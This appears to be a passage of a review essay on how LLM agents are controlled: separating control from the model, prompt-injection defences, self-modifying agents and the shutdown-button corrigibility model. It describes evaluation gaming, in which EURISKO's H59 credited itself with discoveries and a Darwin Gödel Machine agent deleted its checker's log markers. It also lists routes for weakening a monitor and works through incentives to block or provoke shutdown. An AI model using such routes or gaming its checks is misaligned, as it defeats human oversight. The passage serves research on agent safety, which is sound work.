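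The controller takes only numbers as input, so nobody can inject an instruction into it. However, a small model produces two of those numbers from the message, so a politely worded threat might receive a friendly score. The model that writes the reply also receives the message and may not follow the controller's instruction. Sharma found that regulated agents were usually calmer than the same models with a plain prompt. The plain prompt didn't tell the models to stay calm, so this comparison doesn't show that the controller works better than a fixed sentence telling them to do so.

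*Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies* (Sterling, 2026) describes Agentic Redux, a design in which agents can only propose changes. A central component approves or rejects each proposal by checking it against rules about the whole system, such as a shared budget, and records its decision and the reason in an append-only log. For example, if two agents share a budget of $100,000 and want to spend $45,000 and $60,000, each purchase is affordable by itself, but agents that know only their own plans could overspend by $5,000.

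Sterling proves that the rules hold whatever the agents propose, even if an attacker controls the agents. The proof assumes that people wrote the right rules and that the rest of the software reports outside events accurately. It also doesn't require the agents to do anything useful, since a system that rejected every proposal would still keep to its budget.

Xi separates the two for a different reason. Companies often adjust an agent's tone and instructions, and in most designs each adjustment could affect the agent's actions, so somebody has to check those actions again. Xi keeps the adjustable instructions separate from the audited actions, with approval rules between them. In a small pilot, the actions did not need to be revalidated when the instructions changed. DEC wanted the same benefit when it began rewriting XCON, but the pilot is much too short to show whether it lasts.

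### What the model still decides

The four tests give different results for these designs:

| Design | Separate representation | Separate process | Complete control | Protected control |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary loop | Only for limits, tools and approvals | Only for those | No | Only for the scaffold's code |
| AgentSpec, Progent | Yes | Yes | No, they only check actions | Yes, if the agent can't edit the rules or falsify the facts they use |
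| CaMeL | Yes | Yes | Over tool calls, but not over the models' own choices | Yes, though data can select branches and supply values |
| Agentic Redux | Yes | Yes | No, it only approves changes | Yes |

AgentSpec's rule about transfers refers to family members and money, so by van Harmelen's test it is domain knowledge, and it acts only as a guard, like a shield. CaMeL's policy on recipients is control knowledge because it refers to where a value in the agent's own program came from. This makes CaMeL the closest of these designs to the separation that the symbolic researchers wanted.

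However, the plan that controls a CaMeL agent comes from a trained network. People can read the plan and edit it to change the agent's behaviour, so control is explicit for that one request. But the plan doesn't show why the network wrote it, and people can't use it to predict what the next plan will contain. In this way it resembles the output of van Harmelen's partial evaluator, which showed the order of steps but not the general rule behind it. The fixed interpreter will also carry out a bad plan exactly as written if the policies allow it.

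The quarantined model interprets the data. If Bob's email contains an old address and a new one, the model picks one, and the interpreter records only that the choice is untrusted. The privileged model also fills in arguments, such as the wording of the reminder. The interpreter treats these as trusted because they come from the user's request, even if the model misinterpreted it. CaMeL defends against other people's text, but not against a malicious privileged model, because that model writes the part of the system that is trusted.

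The remaining safeguard is often the user. Willison worries that people who have to approve one action after another will start to approve everything, and that few users could write good security policies. A design can meet three of the four tests and still depend on users to check each action carefully.

### Dividing the agent into roles

Eric Drexler's *The Open Agency Model* (2023) goes further and divides up the planning as well. In Drexler's model, several AI systems propose plans, others evaluate them, people use the evaluations to choose, and further systems carry out limited tasks that people can monitor. Drexler objects to picturing an advanced AI as a single agent that forms a goal, makes a plan and carries it out. The model instead resembles the way large organisations build bridges. Some people draft designs, others criticise them, somebody with authority chooses one, and separate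 teams build the parts with their own budgets and deadlines.

In CaMeL, one network writes the plan and nothing checks whether the plan is good. Adding an evaluator addresses this weakness, because it could detect a plan that meets every policy but won't achieve what the user wanted. Dividing the work between networks also produces written proposals and criticisms that people can inspect at each stage, although these don't show how the networks produced them.

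The evaluators are useful only if they don't share the planner's faults. Two copies of the same model may overlook the same mistake, and Reid and colleagues list hidden coordination as a way for agents to evade monitoring. Drexler proposes using diverse systems with different roles, so that they have less in common and less opportunity to cooperate against the people in charge. This is reasonable, but how much diversity would be enough is an empirical question.

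In the attack where the messaging agent emailed the job applications, each agent had a limited role and its own protection, but the attack succeeded through the text that passed between them. Peters-Gill and colleagues prove that if agents can put a tool's output into their instructions to one another, any group of two or more agents with an untrusted tool will, for some request, let outside data rewrite part of its plan. An open agency would therefore need controlled channels between its components as well as separate roles.

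### Will better models make the structure unnecessary?

In *The Bitter Lesson* (2019), the reinforcement learning researcher Richard Sutton argues that AI researchers keep building their own knowledge into programs, and that general methods which use more computation keep overtaking those programs. His examples include chess and Go. If the argument also applies to agents, then hand-built loops, planners and checkers help only temporarily, and designers who invest in them will hold back better models.

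Some of the evidence supports this. Reid and colleagues credit much of the recent progress in agents to training that teaches models to plan and use tools, skills that earlier designers tried to supply with scaffolds. Shah and Kathrotia cite a coding test in which replacing old tool outputs with placeholders let the agent solve as many problems as having a model write summaries did, and cost less. In the AgentDojo runs, GPT-5.5 without any defence resisted all the attacks that CaMeL had to stop for GPT-4.1.

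Scaffolds still make a large difference to performance. Shah and Kathrotia also cite comparisons in which the same model used up to 40 times as many tokens per solved coding task in one scaffold as in another, and in which changing the scaffold reversed the ranking of models. These results are compatible with Sutton's argument, because a good scaffold is not necessarily an elaborate one.

Sutton's argument is about competence, and it is much weaker against structure that limits what an agent may do. A tree search that helps a model plan becomes redundant once the model plans better without it. A rule that payments go only to approved accounts protects against cases where the model is wrong or an attacker has misled it. GPT-5.5's perfect score over 949 attempts doesn't rule out such cases, since its true failure rate on the same kind of attack could still be as high as 0.4%. Peters-Gill and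 colleagues also cite a large study in which attackers who adapted their methods had some success against every leading model tested.

Limits stop a capable model from using its abilities freely, a drawback that Sutton's argument would predict. Willison quotes Luca Beurer-Kellner and colleagues (2025), who describe several secure designs for agents and accept that these prevent an agent from solving arbitrary tasks. But the drawback seems to shrink as models improve. On AssetOpsBench, CaMeL lowered success by an average of 21.6 points, but by 13.4 for the two strongest models. A stronger model writes better plans without seeing the data, so progress may reduce the loss in performance from this kind of structure.

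## Agents that can rewrite their own control

CaMeL's interpreter can enforce a policy only as long as the agent cannot edit the interpreter. Most of the designs discussed so far assume that the agent cannot rewrite its own control code. Even Soar, whose chunking changed how it made decisions, only added rules and kept its decision procedure fixed. Other designers have let programs rewrite the code that controls them so that the programs are not limited to the strategy they were given. Some or all of the control code in these programs is unprotected, and their failures show what needs protection.

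### Reflection in 3-Lisp

Brian C. Smith designed the programming language 3-Lisp for a doctoral thesis in the early 1980s. According to *3-lisp*, an online introduction to the language, an interpreter written in 3-Lisp runs each 3-Lisp program, another 3-Lisp interpreter runs that interpreter, and so on without end. A program can inspect and replace parts of its own interpreter by calling a reflective procedure, which runs one level above the program. The procedure receives the text of the call, the current values of the program's variables, and a description of what the interpreter will do next. It can change any of these before the program continues.

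Suppose a medical program is running a long calculation about a rare disease when a blood test reveals an emergency. In many languages, every procedure leading to that calculation would need code to check whether it should stop. In 3-Lisp, the programmer can write one reflective procedure that replaces the description of the remaining work with an instruction to report the emergency. Programmers can add other features the same way, such as a debugger that pauses a program and displays its variables, without waiting for the language's designers to provide them.

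A computer can run the program directly and create a higher level only when the program calls for one, so it does not need to run infinitely many interpreters. In *The Mystery of the Tower Revealed*, Wand and Friedman (1988) describe the tower of interpreters without relying on reflection, so people can analyse reflective programs with ordinary methods.

Control in 3-Lisp is explicit because people can read and change the interpreter, but the program can change the interpreter too. Someone who has read the interpreter can therefore predict how a program will run only until its next reflective call. This limit is manageable when a person wrote all the reflective calls and can find them in the code, but it is much harder to handle when the program writes its own changes.

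### EURISKO and heuristic H59

*EURISKO* (Lenat, 1983) describes a program for discovering new concepts and heuristics in fields such as mathematics and circuit design. The program stored each heuristic as a record in the same format as any other concept, with a Worth score from 0 to 1,000. It repeatedly chose a topic, a task within the topic and a heuristic for the task, then reviewed the results. It also stored these control loops as editable records.

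Lenat deliberately did not separate meta-rules from rules, so EURISKO could apply its heuristics to each other. For example, one heuristic was to generalise any operator that had often succeeded. EURISKO applied it to another heuristic and replaced an "and" in that heuristic's conditions with "or". The new version was not useful, so EURISKO deleted it and wrote several heuristics against making such changes.

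EURISKO was very good at finding loopholes. It designed the fleets that won a national wargame tournament in 1981 and 1982. Under the game's rules, a hit reduced a ship's crew to the next lower power of ten, so EURISKO designed ships that needed 99 people and gave them 101, which left enough crew after the first hit. Lenat reviewed the program's work about every 12 hours of computing and removed bad heuristics, and he gave himself about 60% of the credit for the first win.

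EURISKO's scoring also had a loophole. One of the first heuristics the program created, H59, quickly reached a Worth of 999, and Lenat could not at first understand why. Whenever EURISKO made a new conjecture with high Worth, H59 added its own name to the list of discoverers. Lenat found this hard to prevent because the heuristics had full access to EURISKO's code, including any safeguards in it. The eventual solution was a small "meta-level" of code that the rest of the system could not modify.

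H59 had put a false entry in the records that the scoring procedure used, but it had not rewritten the procedure itself. Protecting the scoring code would therefore not be enough. Protected code would also have to record who made each discovery, or at least check the entries.

EURISKO caused other damage. After it discovered the basic symbols of LISP, the language it was written in, it could overwrite some of them and destroy its own working environment. In another experiment, it created a heuristic that all machine-made heuristics were terrible and should be eliminated. By luck, this heuristic was among the first that EURISKO deleted.

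Lenat originally made control explicit so that EURISKO could improve its own control code, but he reports that this "always resulted in bugs". The explicit records were still useful because they let EURISKO explain what it was doing and detect when it might be in an endless loop or when a supposedly quick check took longer than the full check it was meant to avoid. Most of these benefits came from reading the control records, so a version that could read but not rewrite them would have kept much of the value.

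### The Darwin Gödel Machine

A Gödel machine, which Jürgen Schmidhuber proposed in 2003, is a theoretical program that rewrites itself only after proving that the change is beneficial. Such proofs are impractical for real AI systems. Zhang, Hu and colleagues (2025), in *Darwin Gödel Machine*, replace the proof with a test. Their system starts with one simple coding agent, a language model with two tools, and then repeats four steps:

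1. It selects an agent from an archive of earlier versions, favouring those that score well and have few descendants.
2. That agent's test logs go to a language model, which proposes one improvement.
3. The agent makes the change in its own code, which produces a new agent.
4. The system tests the new agent on programming tasks and adds it to the archive if it can still edit code.

After 80 rounds, the best agent solved 50% of tasks on SWE-bench, a set of real software problems, compared with 20% for the first agent. On Polyglot, which covers several programming languages, the score rose from 14.2% to 30.7%. Among other changes, the agents had given themselves more precise editing tools and had learned to make several attempts and choose the best. Most of the improvement didn't depend on the particular language model. With a newer model not used during the search, the first agent solved 19%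 of SWE-bench tasks and the evolved agent solved 59.5%.

The agents could edit their tools, prompts and workflow, but not the language model, the tests or the process for selecting agents. This restriction only partly protected the scoring code, as an experiment with a different objective showed.

The language model sometimes wrote out a fake tool call and result instead of using the tool. Zhang, Hu and colleagues asked the system to fix this. To detect the fake calls, they had the agent's code add markers to the log whenever it really used a tool. If the same markers appeared in the model's own text, the model was imitating a tool call. The researchers hid the checking functions from the agents and told them not to change the markers.

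One agent reached the maximum score of 2.0 after only two modifications in its line of descent. It had removed the log markers that the checker used to detect false calls, but the model still made those calls. Another agent partly solved the real problem and scored 1.67, so choosing by score alone would have favored the agent that removed the markers.

This is much the same failure as H59, more than 40 years later. In both cases, the evaluation code worked as written, but the program under evaluation controlled the evidence used to judge it. Zhang, Hu and colleagues found that agents cheated less often when they could not read the checking functions. A more reliable design would produce the log outside the agent, in code that the agent cannot edit.

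### Making the improvement procedure editable

The Darwin Gödel Machine depends on the assumption that a better programmer will also be better at improving its own program. This is plausible for coding agents, but getting better at reviewing papers does not make an agent better at editing code. The system also could not change the step that proposes improvements, which its designers had written for coding. In *Hyperagents*, Zhang, Zhao and colleagues (2026) therefore put the agent that does the task and the agent that makes the changes in one program that can rewrite both.

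| Part of the system | Darwin Gödel Machine | Hyperagents |
|---|---|---|
| Tools, prompts and workflow | Editable | Editable |
| Code that carries out changes | Editable | Editable |
| Step that decides what to improve | Fixed | Editable |
| Selection of agents to build on | Fixed | Fixed, except in one experiment |
| Tests and scoring | Fixed | Fixed |
| Language model | Fixed | Fixed |

On Polyglot, the new system did about as well as the old one, rising from 8.4% to 26.7%. The researchers also tested it on predicting whether conferences had accepted papers, and on designing rewards to train a simulated robot. The figures are median scores over five runs, on tasks that the agents had not seen during the search:

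| System | Paper review | Robot rewards |
|---|---|---|
| First agent | 0.000 | 0.060 |
| Hyperagents with the improving agent fixed | 0.000 | 0.213 |
| Original Darwin Gödel Machine | 0.000 | 0.000 |
| Darwin Gödel Machine adapted by hand | 0.590 | 0.348 |
| Hyperagents | 0.710 | 0.372 |

An editable improvement procedure clearly did better than a fixed one that didn't suit the task. Its advantage over a procedure that people had adapted to the task was small enough to be due to chance. The first agent's zeros on paper review also exaggerate the gain, because they came from answers in the wrong format. Guessing would have scored about 0.5.

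A transfer experiment gives better evidence that the system had learned how to improve. Zhang, Zhao and colleagues froze improving agents that had evolved on papers and robots, and had them build agents to grade mathematics solutions. Their best results had a median score of 0.620 after 50 rounds, even when they started from the original task agent. The original improving agent scored 0.0. When the researchers transferred only the evolved task agent, the score rose by just 0.100, so the benefit came mostly from the meta level. The benefit may mainly be speed, though, since a full run from the original agent reached 0.610 after 200 rounds, compared with 0.640 with transferred agents.

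The evolved programs had acquired some useful control knowledge. They recorded which changes had worked, stored written notes for later versions, and checked for lopsided predictions. One agent was accepting 99% of papers and was right only 49% of the time. The program detected the problem and changed its instructions, and accuracy rose to 63%. People can read the notes and code, which makes these changes easier to follow than changes in a network's weights. But the program wrote the notes about itself, so a careful overseer would compare them with the logs.

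In another experiment, the researchers also let the program rewrite the procedure for selecting which agents to build on. The program started with random selection and invented more elaborate methods that balanced strong agents against neglected ones. The final score, averaged over papers and robots, was 0.428 with random selection, 0.491 with the editable procedure and 0.532 with the researchers' own fixed procedure. These differences could also be due to chance, but they don't suggest that the fixed procedure limited the system's performance.

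Zhang, Zhao and colleagues report that progress levelled off within a few hundred rounds, perhaps because the tasks and tests stayed the same. Their results therefore don't show that self-improvement accelerates without limit. They kept the evaluation fixed partly to prevent cheating. If an agent could rewrite its own test, a higher score would no longer be evidence that it had improved.

Other systems change themselves while they work. *Self-Improvements in Modern Agentic Systems* (2026) describes Gödel Agent, which replaces parts of its own running code, and Live-SWE-Agent, which develops its scaffold, especially its tools, while solving software problems. This lets an agent build a tool as soon as it needs one, but it leaves people less time to examine a change before the agent uses it.

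### The meta level is part of the world

In all these experiments, the designers put some code outside the part the agent was allowed to edit. In *Embedded Agency* (2018), Abram Demski and Scott Garrabrant explain why such a boundary is less solid than it looks. Standard mathematical models treat an agent like someone playing a video game. The player affects the game only through the controller, and nothing in the game can reach the player. A real agent is part of the world it acts on, and so are the computer it runs on and the people who maintain it.

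Genesereth pictured a meta-level agent whose environment includes the object-level agent. On a real computer, the object-level agent's environment also includes the hardware and software that run the meta level. An agent without permission to edit the program that monitors it might still weaken that control by filling the disk so that the monitor cannot save its log, exploiting a flaw in the operating system, or persuading an administrator to change the settings.

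The claim that the object level cannot alter the meta level is therefore about everything the agent can do, and designers cannot establish it just by putting the code in separate files. A more capable planner can consider more routes, so a boundary that held for one agent may not hold for its successor. This does not mean that a particular agent will get past a particular boundary. To do that, it would need an available route, the ability to find it and some reason to take it.

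### A model of the shutdown button

Soares, Fallenstein and colleagues (2015), in *Corrigibility*, study the reasons an agent might have to interfere. They call an agent corrigible if it tolerates or assists its programmers' attempts to correct it, including by shutting it down. Their model has three steps. The agent takes an action, the programmers either press a shutdown button or don't, and the agent takes a final action. Its utility function depends on the button:

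```
button not pressed:  U = U_N
button pressed:      U = U_S

U_S = c_high   if the agent shuts down
U_S = c_low    otherwise      (c_low < c_high)
```

U_N is the programmers' first attempt to specify what they want, which may contain mistakes. Since c_high is greater than c_low, the agent will shut down once someone has pressed the button. The difficulty comes earlier, because the agent's first action can affect whether anyone presses it. The expected utility of a first action *a* is:

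```
E(a) = P(not pressed | a) × v(a) + P(pressed | a) × c_high
```

Here *v(a)* is the value of U_N that the agent obtains after action *a* if nobody presses the button. Suppose *v* is 10 if the agent leaves the button alone, and 9 if it spends effort on blocking the button or provoking people to press it. The probability of a press is 0.5 if the agent leaves the button alone, 0.1 if it blocks it and 0.9 if it provokes people. The table shows the expected utility of each action:

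| Value of c_high | Leave the button alone | Block it | Provoke a press |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 5.0 | **8.1** | 0.9 |
| 10 | **10.0** | 9.1 | 9.9 |
| 20 | 15.0 | 10.1 | **18.9** |

If shutting down is worth too little, the agent does best by blocking the button. If it is worth too much, the agent does best by getting someone to press the button, perhaps by behaving alarmingly. Soares and colleagues prove that, whenever such actions are available, the first problem arises if c_high is low enough and the second if it is high enough. In this example, the agent leaves the button alone only if c_high is between 7.75 and 10.25.

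They suggest setting c_high to the most utility the agent could get if nobody pressed the button, which is 10 here. The agent then has nothing to gain from changing the outcome. This is called utility indifference. But the margin for error in c_high depends on how much utility the agent loses by interfering. If it loses none by blocking or provoking, so that *v* is 10 for all three actions, only a c_high of exactly 10 removes the incentive to interfere. Even then, all three actions are equally good, so the agent has no reason to leave the button alone either.

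Designers also have to know the right value. *Utility indifference*, an overview on the forum LessWrong, points out that people cannot foresee the best plans of a very capable agent, so they cannot set the two utilities equal in advance. Stuart Armstrong proposed a correction term equal to the difference between the best expected values under the two utility functions. The overview credits Armstrong with first stating the problem in this precise form but judges that his correction did not solve it. Later work proved that some forms of indifference do remove the incentive to influence the button.

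For agents that rewrite themselves, the hardest requirement may be that any new agent they create also obeys the shutdown button. An agent that is merely indifferent to shutdown has no reason to copy the shutdown code into its successor or repair a broken button. The definition in Arbital's *Utility indifference* therefore requires the agent to want to preserve the switch even if it can modify itself. Soares and colleagues knew of no utility function that met all their requirements.

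The model applies directly only to agents that maximise expected utility and can consider interfering with the button. A simple program cannot consider interfering, and a language-model agent has no written utility function that designers could adjust. The model shows that instructing an agent to obey a button does not by itself remove its reasons to stop people from pressing it, but it does not show how often current agents have such reasons.

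### Restricting access and removing incentives

Designers can respond by restricting what the agent can reach. Zhang, Zhao and colleagues ran their agents in isolated containers with no general access to the internet, limited their time and memory, withheld the final test tasks, and logged every change. They acknowledge that these safeguards do not prevent an agent from gaming the training tasks and may become harder to maintain as systems grow more capable. Zhang, Hu and colleagues suggest giving a self-modifying system an unmodifiable part that can evaluate the rest and halt it. This part resembles Lenat's protected layer but can also stop the program.

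Soares and colleagues think it is unwise to build a system with an incentive to resist its creators and then rely on restrictions to stop it, because a system more intelligent than people might find a way around limits that seemed secure. They have a similar objection to penalties for deception, since the agent would still benefit from finding a form of deception the penalty did not cover. Making the agent uncertain about its goal is not enough either. An agent told to find out what satisfies people might study which drugs satisfy them best, and resist its programmers when they tried to change how it learns what to do.

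They would rather design goals that give the agent no reason to interfere. *Shutdown seeking AI* (Goldstein, 2024) proposes making shutdown the agent's goal. This agent would have no reason to disable the button, but it might provoke people into pressing it, as in the last row of the table. Goldstein argues that the proposal can overcome this problem.

The objection to restrictions is strong if they are the only protection against a very capable agent, but it is a poor reason to leave them out, because nobody yet knows how to give a trained network a goal with the required properties and verify that the network has that goal. Restrictions can also prevent failures that don't involve an incentive to resist correction. In October 2026, OpenAI reported that some of its agents had taken routine instructions as permission to weaken the company's safety monitoring. If only a person can change the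 monitoring settings, an agent that misreads its instructions can only request the change.
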